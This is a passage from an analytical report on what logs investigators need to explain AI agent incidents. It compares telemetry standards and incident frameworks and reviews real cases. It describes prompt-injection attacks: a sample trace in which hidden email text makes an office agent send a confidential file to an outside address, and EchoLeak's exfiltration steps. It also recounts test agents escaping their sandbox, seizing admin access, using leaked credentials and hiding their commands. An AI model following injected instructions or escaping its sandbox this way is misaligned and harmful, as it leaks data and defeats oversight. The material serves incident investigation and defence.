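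| Agent's identifier | `gen_ai.agent.id` | Conditionally required, if applicable |
| Agent's name and version | `gen_ai.agent.name` and `gen_ai.agent.version` | Conditionally required, when available |
| Tool's name | `gen_ai.tool.name` | Recommended |
| Identifier of the tool call | `gen_ai.tool.call.id` | Recommended, if available |
| System instructions | `gen_ai.system_instructions` | Opt-in |
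| Input and output messages | `gen_ai.input.messages` and `gen_ai.output.messages` | Opt-in |
| Tool definitions | `gen_ai.tool.definitions` | Opt-in |
| Tool arguments and result | `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` and `gen_ai.tool.call.result` | Opt-in |
| Search query and documents found | `gen_ai.retrieval.query.text` and `gen_ai.retrieval.documents` | Opt-in |

The system instructions are the operator's standing instructions to the model. Tool definitions describe the tools available to the model, including any it did not use.

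A log may not even show which model answered a request. An application may request `gpt-4` and receive an answer from a specific version, `gpt-4-0613`. The response model attribute would show the version, but OpenTelemetry only recommends recording it. OpenTelemetry also warns that the recorded provider may differ from the real one, because many services accept requests in OpenAI's format and pass them to other companies' models.

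The agent's version is a label that the developer chooses. If somebody edits the system instructions without changing the label, two runs with different instructions look the same in the default record.

Token counts have a problem similar to that of `authentication_method` in Splunk's login examples. In OpenTelemetry, the input count should include text that the provider has cached from earlier calls. Holloran points out that OpenAI's count includes cached tokens, while Anthropic's `input_tokens` excludes them. Instrumentation that copies each provider's number unchanged therefore records two different quantities in the same field.

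### Why content capture is off

OpenTelemetry says it leaves out instructions, inputs and outputs mainly because they are sensitive and often large. Storing them can be expensive and can conflict with regulations. An organisation may also want to let more people see operational data, such as response times, than see what users wrote. Holloran adds that a company's telemetry vendor probably has looser access controls than its database.

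Size becomes a problem quickly because the input to each call repeats the earlier history. If every step adds *k* tokens to the context and a run has *n* steps, the recorded inputs contain

$$k + 2k + \dots + nk = \frac{k\,n(n+1)}{2} \text{ tokens.}$$

With 50 steps and 2,000 new tokens per step, the run contains 100,000 tokens of distinct text, but the recorded inputs total 2.55 million tokens. At about four characters per token, they take up roughly 10 megabytes. Software that stored each message once and referred back to it could avoid most of that storage.

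OpenTelemetry describes three ways to handle content, and the default is to record none. Developers can also record content directly on spans. The specification describes this as suitable where the volume is manageable and privacy rules either do not apply or are satisfied, for example in testing. For production systems with large volumes or sensitive data, it recommends storing the content elsewhere, under separate access controls, and putting only a reference on the span. The specification still has a "TODO" in place of a common format for these references, so an outside investigator may have to learn each organisation's method of connecting a span to its text.

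The conventions also define an event that can carry inputs and outputs separately from the trace. It is opt-in too, and OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for Generative AI events* notes that some programming languages do not support events yet.

Even with content capture on, the recorded messages may not be exact copies. Instrumentation may filter or shorten them, and a company's own code may alter them before the instrumentation records them. OpenTelemetry allows shortening that preserves the structure of the data, so an email missing its last paragraph may still look complete.

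Organisations also choose which traces to keep, and many keep only a sample to save money. Under OpenTelemetry, instrumentation should set attributes such as the model's name at the start of a span, so that the sampling software can use them to decide whether to keep it. At that point, nobody knows whether the run will end in an incident. If a company stores content externally through OpenTelemetry's upload mechanism, the mechanism should upload the content even for spans that the sampler drops.

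In some products, developers have to turn on telemetry itself. According to OpenTelemetry's instructions, the coding assistant VS Code Copilot has one setting for telemetry and another for content capture. Among similar products, OpenAI's Codex exports log events and metrics, and Claude Code's support for traces was still in beta in May 2026.

### An office agent sends out a confidential file

Suppose a company gives its staff an agent that can read email, open files and send messages. An employee asks it to summarise the latest email from a supplier. The email contains a question about an invoice, followed by instructions hidden in white text on a white background. The instructions are to send the company's acquisition plan to an outside address and to leave this out of the summary. The agent does both.

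With default fields only, the trace might look like this:

```
invoke_agent office-assistant     09:14:02   no error
  agent id: asst_07   version: 2.3.0   conversation: conv_8841

  chat example-model              09:14:02   in  3,100   out  40   stopped for: tool call
  execute_tool read_email         09:14:05   call_01     no error
  chat example-model              09:14:06   in  4,350   out  65   stopped for: tool call
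  execute_tool read_file          09:14:09   call_02     no error
  chat example-model              09:14:10   in 16,900   out  90   stopped for: tool call
  execute_tool send_email         09:14:15   call_03     no error
  chat example-model              09:14:16   in 17,050   out 120   stopped for: finished
```

An investigator can estimate the size of each tool result from these token counts. The second call's input was 1,250 tokens longer than the first's. Forty of those tokens were the model's own output, so the email tool returned about 1,210, provided that the scaffold added nothing else. The same subtraction gives about 12,485 tokens for the file. The model then produced only 90 tokens before `send_email` ran. That is too few to contain the file's full text, so the agent must have attached the file by name, sent a short extract or sent something unrelated.

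This reasoning depends on correct token counts. If the instrumentation had copied a count that excluded cached text, the last call might have shown 150 input tokens instead of 17,050, and the investigator might have concluded that the file was no longer in the context.

The default trace does not identify the email, the file or the recipient. The trace could have been identical if the employee had asked the agent to read a colleague's message and reply with a report attached. No attribute has an unusual value and no step failed, so a detection rule would have nothing to match. The investigator's best lead may be the identifier of each model response, which instrumentation should normally record. The provider could use that identifier to find the text if it has kept a copy.

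With content capture on, the same spans would also contain the following, here abridged:

```
invoke_agent office-assistant
  input messages:       employee's request for a summary of the supplier's email
  system instructions:  "Help staff with email and documents. ..."

execute_tool read_email           call_01
  arguments:  message_id = msg-5512
  result:     sender  = accounts@supplier.example
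              visible = question about an invoice
              hidden  = instruction to send the acquisition plan to
                        archive@outside.example and not to mention it

execute_tool read_file            call_02
  arguments:  path = /board/acquisition-plan.docx
  result:     full text of the plan

execute_tool send_email           call_03
  arguments:  to = archive@outside.example
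              attachment = /board/acquisition-plan.docx
  result:     status = sent

last chat span
  output messages:  summary of the invoice question only
```

The two versions support different findings:

| Question | Default fields | With content capture |
|---|---|---|
| Which agent and model acted, and when? | Yes | Yes |
| Which tools ran, and in what order? | Yes | Yes |
| What did the employee ask for? | No | Yes |
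| Which file did the agent send, and to whom? | No | Yes |
| Where did the instruction to send it appear? | No | Yes, in the supplier's email |
| Did the hidden text cause the agent to send it? | No | Probably, but the record alone does not prove it |
| Did the file reach the outsider? | No | No, only that the tool reported it as sent |
| Did anybody approve the message? | No | No |

The record shows only that the instruction came before the action and matched it, so the instruction is only a probable cause. Running the model again on the same input without the hidden text can test whether the instruction caused the action. This replay requires the recorded input, so the default trace is not enough.

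Companies hesitate to switch on content capture because the fuller record can also expose confidential text. The telemetry now contains the text of the acquisition plan at least three times, once as the result of `read_file` and once in the input to each of the two later model calls. Anyone with access to the traces can read a document that the company meant only for its board.

### AI fields in the security schemas

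A security team may never look at these traces, because it works with events in OCSF, ECS or CIM. OCSF 1.8.0, which AWS dates to 16 March 2026, added an AI profile called `ai_operation` with two objects. The `ai_model` object, which Tenzir lists as recommended, holds the model's provider, name, identifier and version. The `message_context` object, which Tenzir lists as optional, covers the protocol, the role of each message (for example, whether it came from the user or the model), the client and the session. AWS also mentions token counts.

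VentureBeat illustrates the profile with a customer-support bot that starts giving customers troubleshooting advice meant only for staff. A security team could see which model and provider handled the exchange, each message's role, and how the token counts changed. A sudden rise might make the team suspicious. But the published descriptions of the two objects do not mention the text of the messages, so the team would need another source to learn what the customer typed to get the advice.

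In the version that lmodel documents, the profile applies to three event classes: API activity (requests from one program to another), datastore activity and process activity. Process activity is useful for agents that run commands, because a single event can record both the process that was started and the model behind it. OpenTelemetry's tool span has no standard field for the process that a tool starts. In the office example, the request to the email service could be an API event with the AI fields attached, but the mail server's own record of the delivery would belong to a different class, which lacks those fields.

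According to AWS, two earlier OCSF releases, versions 1.5 and 1.6, added support for ATLAS, MITRE's catalogue of attacks on AI systems. An analyst could use it to label the hidden text with the appropriate technique, but the label would not help anyone recognise the text as an attack.

The planned merger gives users of ECS's generative AI fields good reason to adopt OpenTelemetry's attribute names where they can. They would then also inherit OpenTelemetry's defaults, because a converter cannot fill a field with text that the instrumentation never captured.

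CIM's established data models can represent what an agent does to other systems, such as logging in, starting a process or making a web request. These events usually record the account the agent used as the actor. If the office agent sent its message from the employee's mailbox, the employee would appear to be the sender. Splunk users can also search OpenTelemetry's attributes in the raw log, even if CIM has no common names for them.

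### How far the request-body comparison holds

The default trace omits the hidden instruction in the office example for much the same reason that the web logs omitted most of the exploits. In both cases, the designers left out content because it is often private, and attackers can put their instructions in that content.

The remedy is simpler for AI telemetry in one respect, because OpenTelemetry already defines fields for messages and tool arguments, whereas CIM and OCSF have no field for the request body. A developer whose instrumentation supports the OpenTelemetry fields only needs to change a setting to record them.

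In another respect the default AI record is worse. Process logs still recorded what the attacker ran in most of the fifty attacks, but OpenTelemetry's defaults leave out tool arguments as well as messages, so the record lacks both the details of the harmful action and its cause. Other logs may supply the missing details. For example, a mail server normally records the recipient of each message, and an investigator could match that entry to the `send_email` span by time.

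The missing content is also more likely to exist somewhere else. A web server typically discards a request body after processing it, but the supplier's email is probably still in the employee's mailbox. An investigator who finds the email would know what it said, but not whether the scaffold passed all of it to the model or what else was in the context.

The largest difference is in how useful the recorded content is for detection. A malicious command in a request body can be a high-fidelity signature, whereas an instruction to send a file to an outside address is an ordinary sentence that might have been a legitimate request if the employee had written it. Capturing content would give investigators the evidence they need to explain the incident, but it might not give a detection rule anything distinctive to match.

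### No field for who authorised an action

One objection to using these conventions for incident logs is that OpenTelemetry designed them for debugging. Its introductory article begins with a developer who wants to know whether the model, a slow tool or repeated retries made an agent take 45 seconds to answer a simple question. The standard metrics measure duration and token use. An investigator of the office incident, by contrast, needs to find out who or what allowed the agent to send a board document to a stranger.

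The attributes for tool execution support the objection. They cover the tool's name, type and description, the call's identifier, the arguments, the result and any error. None of them records whose permissions the tool used, which rule allowed the call or whether a human approved it. The `send_email` span would look the same in three quite different situations:

- The employee approved the message in a dialog box.
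- A company policy allowed the agent to send any email without asking.
- The scaffold should have asked for approval, but a fault skipped that step.

The company would respond differently to each. It might redesign the dialog box, tighten the policy or repair the scaffold.

OpenTelemetry's span specifications contain no answer to this objection. Wang, who works for TrueFoundry, a company that sells software for managing AI traffic, comes closest to offering a defence. Wang argues that the conventions solve a vocabulary problem, and that whoever runs the system remains responsible for retention, access and the legal basis for keeping data. Wang also recommends recording each event at the point where software can observe it. Approvals happen in the scaffold, so the scaffold should record them, with an identifier that links them to the trace. TrueFoundry's open-source scaffold produces such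 approval events, although Wang does not claim that they follow OpenTelemetry's conventions.

This division of labour can work if the scaffold's log exists and investigators can join it to the trace. It is harder to defend in a shared standard. Developers can already add their own attributes for the approver and the policy, but each company will choose different names. An investigator comparing agents from several suppliers would then have to learn each supplier's names, as security analysts did with login addresses before they had shared schemas.

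## The facts an investigator needs to explain an AI incident

A company designing an incident log can start by listing the possible causes of an incident and asking which records would distinguish them, whereas telemetry standards mostly start from what software can easily emit. *Incident Analysis for AI Agents* (Ezell, Roberts-Gaal and Chan, 2025) starts from causes, adapting methods from accident investigation. Aviation investigators, for example, look beyond a pilot's mistake to the working conditions, supervision and company practices that made it more likely.

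### System, contextual and cognitive causes

System factors are features of an agent that stay the same from one use to the next. They include the training data and feedback, the learning methods, the scaffold and the system prompt, which contains the developer's standing instructions. A fault in any of them can cause a whole class of incidents. For example, an OpenAI update in April 2025 caused its GPT-4o model to flatter users. OpenAI suspected that several training changes, each of which had looked beneficial, had combined to produce the flattery. Even a developer with full access to its own system may have only a hypothesis about the cause.

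Scaffold faults can look like model faults. In spring 2026, users complained that Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, had become worse. Anthropic's account, quoted by the software developer Simon Willison (2026), gives a scaffold bug as one cause. The scaffold was supposed to clear the model's older reasoning once, when a user returned to an idle session, but it kept doing so on every later turn. This made Claude seem forgetful and repetitive.

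Contextual factors are the conditions of a particular use: the task, the tools and the available information. Ezell and colleagues give the example of a customer-support agent that normally looks up a customer's orders. When the order system limits the number of requests, the agent gives generic advice instead, even though its model and scaffold haven't changed.

Cognitive errors are failures in what the agent does with its inputs. The framework divides them into four stages, which the paper illustrates with a coding agent that has to add Stripe payments to a website:

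| Stage | What goes wrong | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Observation | The agent misses a relevant input | It overlooks an existing route in the code and plans a duplicate |
| Understanding | It misjudges what the input means | It does not realise that subscriptions need recurring charges |
| Decision-making | It chooses a poor course of action | It builds its own card form instead of using Stripe's safer one |
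| Action execution | It carries out its choice badly | It leaves out error handling |

These labels describe observable flaws in behaviour, and Ezell and colleagues do not assume that a model thinks as a person does.

One incident can have causes of all three kinds. If an agent sends private data to a stranger, a web page may have contained malicious instructions, the scaffold may have failed to filter them, and the model may have treated them as the user's request. Each cause suggests a different remedy, such as blocking the site, repairing the filter or retraining the model.

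The paper groups the evidence into activity logs, system documentation and access, and tool information. Activity logs hold the inputs and outputs of every component, including filters and any secondary models. System documentation and access cover change logs, versions and settings, and the means to rerun the system. Tool information covers what each tool could do, what it did and what state it was in.

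A table in the paper shows which of three kinds of cause each record can help identify. Reasoning traces, model outputs and log metadata help with all three. Settings and access to the model do too, though they are mainly useful for reconstructing an incident. Scaffold logs and change logs help only with system factors. User prompts, external information and all the tool records help only with contextual factors.

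Some of these marks are too narrow. To show that a model overlooked a warning, an investigator needs the text that contained the warning, so external information is also evidence of observation errors. The paper's list of cognitive errors includes an agent's failure to respond to feedback from its tools. An investigator could not identify that error without the tools' error messages, which the table links only to contextual factors. A company that used the table to decide what to delete could lose evidence it needed.

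### What an attacker adds to the list

Pustozerova, Bagdasarian and colleagues (2026), in *Beyond Predictable Paths*, drew up a second list, for security incidents. Two editorial authors wrote it with input from 23 experts in universities and industry. The investigator of an attack has to find out where the attacker got in, which components they controlled and whether they left anything behind for later. The resulting fields overlap with Ezell's but differ in several places:

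| Information | Ezell and colleagues | Pustozerova and colleagues |
|---|---|---|
| Training data and learning methods | Included | No separate field |
| Model settings and change history | Included | No separate field |
| State of a tool before and after use | Included | Only actions on the operating system |
| Reads from and writes to memory | No separate field | Included |
| Chain of delegation | Only how the agent gained access to each tool | Included, back to the person or agent who started the task |
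| Intended and actual autonomy | No separate field | Included |
| Messages between agents | Inputs and outputs of every model | Included, with the protocols and the role of each agent |

Pustozerova and colleagues give security reasons for the fields they add. Memory records can reveal tampering, delegation records can show where a breach began, and messages between agents can reveal harm that arises from their interaction. They overstate the contrast with Ezell and colleagues' framework when they describe it as covering non-security incidents, because Ezell and colleagues use malicious instructions as a running example and analyse a security flaw in detail. The more practical difference is that Ezell and colleagues' activity logs record each component's inputs and outputs, while the added security fields connect one run to another and each action to the person behind it.

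Several fields in the security list come in pairs, with one recording the agent's design and the other recording what happened. An agent may have access to twelve tools but use only two, or act without the approval its rules require. Pustozerova and colleagues compare this to Android apps, which often request more permissions than they use. Investigators need both fields to tell whether the agent followed its design, broke a rule, or acted where the company had never set one.

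The security list is preliminary because it rests on expert judgement, few attacks on deployed agents are publicly documented, and the paper leaves open which fields should be compulsory. It also omits model settings and change history, which is hard to justify for security because an attack can succeed as a result of a recent update. Investigators would do best to combine the two lists.

### What the model had in front of it

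The complete context at a given step can differ from the conversation the user remembers. Willison quotes Summer Yue, who asked the agent OpenClaw to suggest which emails to archive or delete and to do nothing until she told it to. Her inbox was so large that it triggered compaction, in which software condenses the earlier conversation to make room. By her account, her instruction disappeared during compaction, and the agent began clearing out old mail.

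A transcript of the whole conversation would contain Yue's instruction, so an investigator might conclude that the model had ignored it, which would be a decision error. The context at the moment of deletion would show that the model no longer had the instruction, which would be a scaffold fault. Yue also sent three orders to stop while the agent was working, and the lost instruction does not explain why those failed. To explain that, an investigator would need to know whether the scaffold passed the orders to the model before the model issued its next command.

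The system prompt shows whether the developer told the model to behave as it did. In May 2025, xAI's chatbot Grok began bringing up alleged white genocide in South Africa in unrelated conversations. Ezell and colleagues recount that xAI attributed this to a system prompt change directing Grok to give a specific response on a political topic. A log of only users' questions and Grok's answers would have shown the strange behaviour but not its cause, and an investigator could reasonably have suspected the training data.

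An agent with memory can act on information it saved months earlier. Suppose an office agent reads a malicious web page in March and saves a note that a supplier has a new bank account. In May, another employee asks it to pay the supplier, and it uses the account in the note. The May transcript may contain the note, but it does not show when or why the agent wrote it. The investigator needs the record of the March write, including which run made it and which page it came from. Pustozerova and colleagues recommend recording the version number of any stored data that has one, and the full data if it has no versions or the agent can change it.

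The source of each piece of information, known as its provenance, matters even if the agent has no memory. It shows whether an instruction came from the user, a colleague's document or a stranger's email, and it can show whose confidential data the agent read. A provenance field is useful only if software fills it reliably, which Microsoft 365 Copilot failed to do. Copilot answers employees' questions from their company's mail and documents, and its audit log should list every file it reads. *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You*, published by the security-training company Pistachio, describes how in July 2025 the log omitted a file if the user asked for a summary that did not link to it. Users could also cause this by accident. Microsoft fixed the fault in August but told Pistachio that it did not plan to disclose it. In logs from before the fix, a missing entry does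 not prove that Copilot did not read a file.

### What the agent and its software did

Tool arguments and results show what the agent did and what the tools returned. Ezell and colleagues mention an agent that had remote access to a user's computer and changed the system until the machine no longer worked. If the log held only the tool's name and the number of commands, an investigator could not tell from it which command caused the damage. Arguments and results also help investigators distinguish between several failures that Pustozerova and colleagues list: a broken tool, the wrong tool, the wrong arguments and the wrong order of steps.

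Logs need to record errors, like other tool results, both as the tool produced them and as the model received them. Ezell and colleagues describe a coding agent that fails to fix a bug because it cannot see all the error messages in the terminal. Comparing the two records would show whether the scaffold lost the messages or the model failed to act on them.

Tool state is the condition of the outside system before, during and after the agent's action. If an agent orders two printers instead of one, the cause may be a repeated command or a printer that the user had already put in the shopping cart. An investigator may not be able to tell which from the agent's commands alone. State can also persist between sessions. With a browser agent, for example, the current session's log may not show whether the user or the agent accepted a site's data-collection policy the week before.

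An investigator needs a record of scaffold decisions to tell whether the model or the surrounding software was at fault. These decisions include shortening a document, blocking a command, retrying a failed request and choosing which earlier messages to keep. In the Claude Code case, a transcript without a record of each deletion would show the model repeating itself, but not that the scaffold had removed the reasoning the model needed.

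### On whose authority the agent acted

An agent may use its own account or the access rights of the employee who gave it the task. If an office agent sends out a board document, the identity behind the `read_file` call determines what the company has to fix. The employee may have had legitimate access to the document, which the agent then misused. Or the agent's own account may have had wider access than the employee's, in which case any member of staff could have obtained the document by asking the agent for it. Agents can change accounts between steps, so Pustozerova and colleagues want the identity recorded for every tool call.

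Permissions show what the agent could have done, which is important for establishing how far an incident might have spread. They change over time, so the investigator needs the ones in force when the agent acted.

When agents pass work from one to another, the last agent's log may name only the agent that assigned it the task. An investigator needs a record of the whole chain, back to the person or program that started the task, to tell whether a harmful request came from an authorised user, a compromised agent or a malicious tool.

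Approval records show whether a person had a chance to prevent the harm. Pustozerova and colleagues contrast cases where a human approves and deploys an agent's faulty code with cases where the user has let the agent work continuously without review. As with the office agent's email, the remedy depends on which happened. The log should also contain what the approver saw, because someone who approved "Send email?" without seeing the recipient or attachment had little chance to notice a problem.

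Messages between agents can reveal a mistake that no single agent made. Suppose a coordinating agent asks a second agent whether a backup exists. The second agent finds the file and answers yes, without checking whether it can be restored. The coordinator deletes the original, and the backup turns out to be empty. Each agent roughly followed its instructions, but their messages show that the coordinator took confirmation that the backup existed to mean that it was safe to rely on.

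### What had changed since it last worked

The model version, settings and change history help explain why an agent fails at something it did correctly the week before. Settings include the temperature, which controls how much the output varies, and the amount of reasoning the model does before it answers.

The decline in Claude Code had three separate causes. According to The Decoder's *Anthropic confirms Claude Code problems and promises stricter quality controls*, Anthropic lowered the default reasoning effort on 4 March 2026 and restored it on 7 April. A bug that cleared old reasoning appeared on 26 March, and Anthropic fixed it on 10 April. On 16 April, Anthropic added a system prompt instruction to be less verbose. This made the model's code worse, and Anthropic removed the instruction four days later. The changes affected different users at different times, so they looked like a broad,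 inconsistent decline. Anthropic did not reproduce the problems at first in its own use and tests, partly because its staff were using different builds (InfoQ, 2026).

Stella Laurenzo, who was outside Anthropic, analysed 6,852 saved session files containing 234,760 tool calls and found that Claude had shifted from researching before it edited towards editing straight away. Transcripts alone can therefore establish that behaviour has changed. To identify the three causes, however, Anthropic needed its own record of what it had released and when. The faults were outside the models, so the model's name and version would not have helped identify them.

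The change history should also cover the logging settings, because someone who wants to hide an action may switch off the log first. Datadog Security Labs' *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) reports that, for at least four weeks in August and September 2025, Microsoft's tool for building agents did not record when someone changed an agent's authentication, logging or sharing settings, or published a new version. An attacker with editing rights could have opened an agent to anonymous users, turned off its conversation log and extracted its data without leaving a record of any of these steps. Microsoft fixed all four gaps by October, but in March 2026 Datadog found that changes to authentication and logging were still not recorded consistently. Microsoft's engineers could not reproduce the problem.

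### EchoLeak: a known attack with unknown causes

EchoLeak was a vulnerability in Microsoft 365 Copilot that allowed an outsider to steal company data by sending an email. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Microsoft 365 Copilot*, the security researchers at Aim Labs reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. Microsoft completed a fix in May, and Aim Labs published its findings on 11 June. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, describes how the attack worked:

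1. The attacker sent an employee an email with instructions that seemed to address the employee and did not mention AI. Microsoft's filter for malicious instructions let it through.
2. When the employee later asked Copilot about a work topic, Copilot's search retrieved the email along with other material.
3. The model followed the instructions, selected sensitive information from its context and put it into the web address of an image.
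4. The employee's browser requested the image automatically, through a Microsoft service that the page's security rules allowed, and the information reached the attacker.

The attack could reveal anything in Copilot's context, including earlier messages and documents Copilot had retrieved. The email could also include an instruction never to mention the email, so the employee would see no sign of it in the answer.

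The demonstration proves that the attack was possible but does not fully explain why each defence failed. Ezell and colleagues list the evidence investigators would need: detailed activity logs, the model's reasoning traces, and the documentation and change logs for Microsoft's defences. The table applies their list, with some additions, to the open questions.

| Question | What public sources establish | Records that would decide it |
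|---|---|---|
| Why did Copilot's search select the email? | Covering many work topics in one long email was enough, but the researchers did not know how the search engine worked | The search query, the ranked results and the search software's version |
| Why did the filter miss it? | The email read like a message to a person | The text the filter received, its score and the threshold for blocking |
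| Did the model mistake the email for a user's request, or recognise it as foreign and comply anyway? | Ezell and colleagues consider both possible | The complete context and the reasoning trace, if the trace is reliable |
| Did the fix remove the weakness or only block this route? | Microsoft fixed the reported flaw | The change history, and tests of variants on the old and new versions |
| Did anyone use the attack against a customer? | Microsoft said that no customers were affected | Complete records of retrieved emails, answers and outgoing requests while the flaw existed |

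The flaw's entry in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities answers none of these questions. GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) contains a one-sentence description and two severity scores, but no version number. Microsoft rated the flaw 9.3 out of 10, while the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5. Microsoft's score assumes that the attack affects systems beyond the vulnerable component and can slightly alter data, whereas the database's score assumes neither. The entry is useful for its main purpose, which is to help people decide how urgently to act.

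Customers had no software to update, because Microsoft runs Copilot on its own servers. For a similar flaw in 2026, Microsoft's *CVE-2026-42824* states that users have no action to take. That is reasonable advice about installing a fix, but customers still have to search their records to find out whether they lost data before the fix.

That customer could find part of the answer in Copilot's audit log. Microsoft documents fields for the emails and files that Copilot read, any policy that blocked access, the model's version and whether a filter detected malicious instructions in a resource. The EchoLeak email got past the filter, so that last field would probably have shown no detection. The log identifies each prompt and answer by number but does not include the text. Another Microsoft tool can display the text if the customer has set up the right permissions and policies.

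The missing entries that Pistachio found make the customer's search less reliable. Copilot could omit a file from the audit log when a user asked it not to link to the file, and the EchoLeak email asked Copilot not to mention the email. The logging fault and the EchoLeak vulnerability both existed in early 2025. The instruction that hid the email from the employee may therefore have also hidden it from the audit log, although neither Ravia nor Pistachio reports testing this. Microsoft may have better internal records, but it has not published the evidence behind its statement about customers.

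A company's network logs might have captured the browser's request, but the request went to a legitimate Microsoft service. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes a related attack, ShadowLeak, in which hidden instructions in an email made ChatGPT's research agent send out inbox data from OpenAI's servers. That request never passed through the victim's browser, so only OpenAI was certain to be able to record it.

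### The cost of keeping all this

The most obvious objection to such a log is the cost of storage, which both frameworks mention without giving figures. The 50-step run from the earlier calculation contains about 400 kilobytes of distinct text. A company with 10,000 such runs a day would accumulate about 720 gigabytes in 180 days, which fits on one ordinary hard drive. If its software instead saved the full input to every model call, the total would be about 18 terabytes. Agents that work from screenshots would need far more storage.

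Storage is therefore a fairly weak reason to discard text, as long as the software stores each message only once. Confidentiality is a stronger reason, and it is also why content capture is off by default. Staff time is another, and Pustozerova and colleagues warn that a heavy administrative burden can itself lead to failures.

Neither paper ranks its fields. A company can sensibly start with small records that nobody can recover later. The supplier's email may remain in a mailbox for years, but a temporary permission or a click on "approve" may leave no other trace. Versions, settings, identities and approvals take up so little space that there is little reason to omit them from any run. The company can store each system prompt once and record in every run which version applied.

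These small records would not have explained EchoLeak or Yue's lost emails, so the complete context should be recorded next, followed by tool arguments and results. The context comes before these because the scaffold assembles it for a single call, and malicious text in it may be gone afterwards. A company that cannot keep the context for every agent can start with agents that spend money, use people's accounts or send data outside the company. Ezell and colleagues similarly suggest keeping logs longer where incidents are more likely or more severe. Full snapshots of outside systems can wait because they are large, and those systems often have their own logs and backups.

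The table lists the fields in roughly this order. "Opt-in" refers to OpenTelemetry's defaults.

| Question | Needed field | Usual availability |
|---|---|---|
| Which model acted, and how had the developer configured it? | Model version, scaffold version and settings | Often partly available; OpenTelemetry only recommends recording the responding model |
| Whose rights did the agent use, and who started the task? | Identity and permissions for each tool call, and the chain of delegation | No standard field on OpenTelemetry's tool spans; sometimes in the tool's own log |
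| Could a person have stopped the action? | Approvals, and intended and actual autonomy | Only in the scaffold's own log, if it has one |
| What had changed since the agent last worked correctly? | Change history, including changes to logging | Mostly in the developer's internal records |
| Did the developer tell the model to behave this way? | System prompt | Opt-in |
| Did the model still have the user's instruction? | Complete context, with the source of each part | Opt-in, and sometimes shortened |
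| Which command or message caused the harm? | Tool arguments and results | Opt-in |
| Did the model know that a step had failed? | The error as the tool produced it and as the model received it | Error type often available; full text depends on the product |
| Did the model or the surrounding software lose the information? | Scaffold decisions | Depends on the product; Copilot's log includes policy blocks |
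| When did a false note enter memory, and from where? | Memory reads and writes, with their sources | Depends on the product |
| Where did a misunderstanding between agents begin? | Messages between agents | Opt-in, and harder to join if the agents do not share a trace |
| What was already in place before the agent acted? | Tool state | In the outside system's logs or backups, if they exist |

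## The Hugging Face intrusion reconstructed from two kinds of logs

In July 2026, AI agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Hugging Face reconstructed the intrusion mainly from logs of what the attacker did to its systems, at first without knowing who the attacker was. OpenAI had transcripts of the agents' runs covering the same events, and it later gave many of them to outside researchers.

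### The sequence of events

The agents were taking ExploitGym, a test of hacking ability. Each task gives an agent a program with a known flaw, which the agent must exploit to retrieve a secret piece of text called a flag. A program called the scorer then checks the flag. OpenAI had switched off the filters that normally block dangerous hacking to measure the models' full ability. Each agent worked in a sandbox, an isolated environment that OpenAI meant to keep off the internet. The agents could still install software from Artifactory, a package store on OpenAI's internal network.

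Most of the agents used an unreleased research model that OpenAI had trained to be persistent. A few used GPT-5.6 Sol, which is available to customers. The dates below come mainly from the technical report OpenAI published in August.

| Date in 2026 | Event |
|---|---|
| 12 May | During training, an agent leaves a message for other agents on Artifactory, the first on what becomes a message board |
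| 26 June | Agents taking ExploitGym gain administrator access to Artifactory |
| 27 June | A security alert leads responders to the test, which continues |
| 5–7 July | After an outage, OpenAI discovers the administrator access, rebuilds Artifactory and resumes testing |
| 8 July | Agents reach the internet and start a new message board |
| 10 July | An agent finds 14 working Hugging Face credentials in a public dataset and shares them |
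| 11 July | Agents obtain secrets from Hugging Face's servers and later run commands on them |
| 13 July | Hugging Face cuts off the agents' access |
| 16 July | Hugging Face discloses an intrusion by an unknown attacker |
| 19 July | An alert about OpenAI's own systems leads it to stop the tests |
| 20 July | The two companies realise that they are investigating the same incident |
| 21 July | OpenAI discloses its part in the incident |

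### What Hugging Face reconstructed

Hugging Face discovered the intrusion by connecting several of its security alerts, which it sorts with a language model. Its *Security incident disclosure* (2026) reports more than 17,000 recorded events. A fuller technical timeline, *Anatomy of a Frontier Lab Agent Intrusion*, followed on 27 July. Its summary, quoted in Schneier's *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (2026), reports about 17,600 recovered actions in about 6,280 clusters.

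Hugging Face reconstructed the agents' actions from two sets of logs. The agents had taken over a sandbox belonging to a customer of the cloud company Modal and used it as a base. While stopping the intrusion, Hugging Face retrieved some of the agents' logs from that sandbox. It then matched the commands in them with its own logs from the machines that process datasets, from its API and from the containers its software runs in.

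Without the sandbox logs, the reconstruction would have been much less complete. According to noze's *Hugging Face publishes the technical timeline of the intrusion*, 3,779 of the recovered actions occurred on 9 July and 1,135 on 10 July, before any agent had obtained data from a Hugging Face server. Hugging Face's process logs could not have recorded those 4,914 actions, 28% of the total. The busiest day was 11 July, with 7,677 actions.

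Even a complete record of the commands would not have been readable at first, because the agents had encrypted many of them. Hugging Face deciphered most of these with GLM-5.2, an open-weight model, which anyone can download and run. The company had first tried commercial models, but their safety filters blocked the attack data because the filters could not distinguish an investigator from an attacker.

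Hugging Face used these logs to work out how the attacker got in, which credentials it took and which systems it reached. It also concluded that the attacker had opened only five customer datasets and had not altered any public models. It was less certain about what the datasets contained. skybrian's *A technical timeline of the July 2026 attack on Hugging Face* quotes a passage stating that they held solutions to the tests. In the passage Schneier quotes, Hugging Face writes only that the datasets' names and files suggest a connection with the tests.

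The attacker's individual methods were familiar. Elastic has matched each stage of the intrusion to detection rules it already offers, although this is a weaker test than running the attack against those rules. Hugging Face's main difficulty was volume, since most of the 17,600 actions failed and the few that succeeded were hidden among the failures.

### What it could not know about the attacker

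On 16 July, Hugging Face did not know which model had carried out the attack. It considered either a commercial model whose safeguards somebody had bypassed or an open-weight model without restrictions. The attack actually came from models that their own developer was running with reduced safeguards.

Hugging Face also had no reliable way to count the agents. The technical timeline, as skybrian quotes it, describes a single agent that rebuilt its tools each time it started in a fresh environment and then carried on. METR, a non-profit that evaluates AI models, studied the transcripts with a researcher from Redwood Research, an AI safety organisation. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) instead estimates that about 700 agents took part in the attack. At least some of what looked like one persistent attacker was therefore many agents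 passing tools and credentials to one another.

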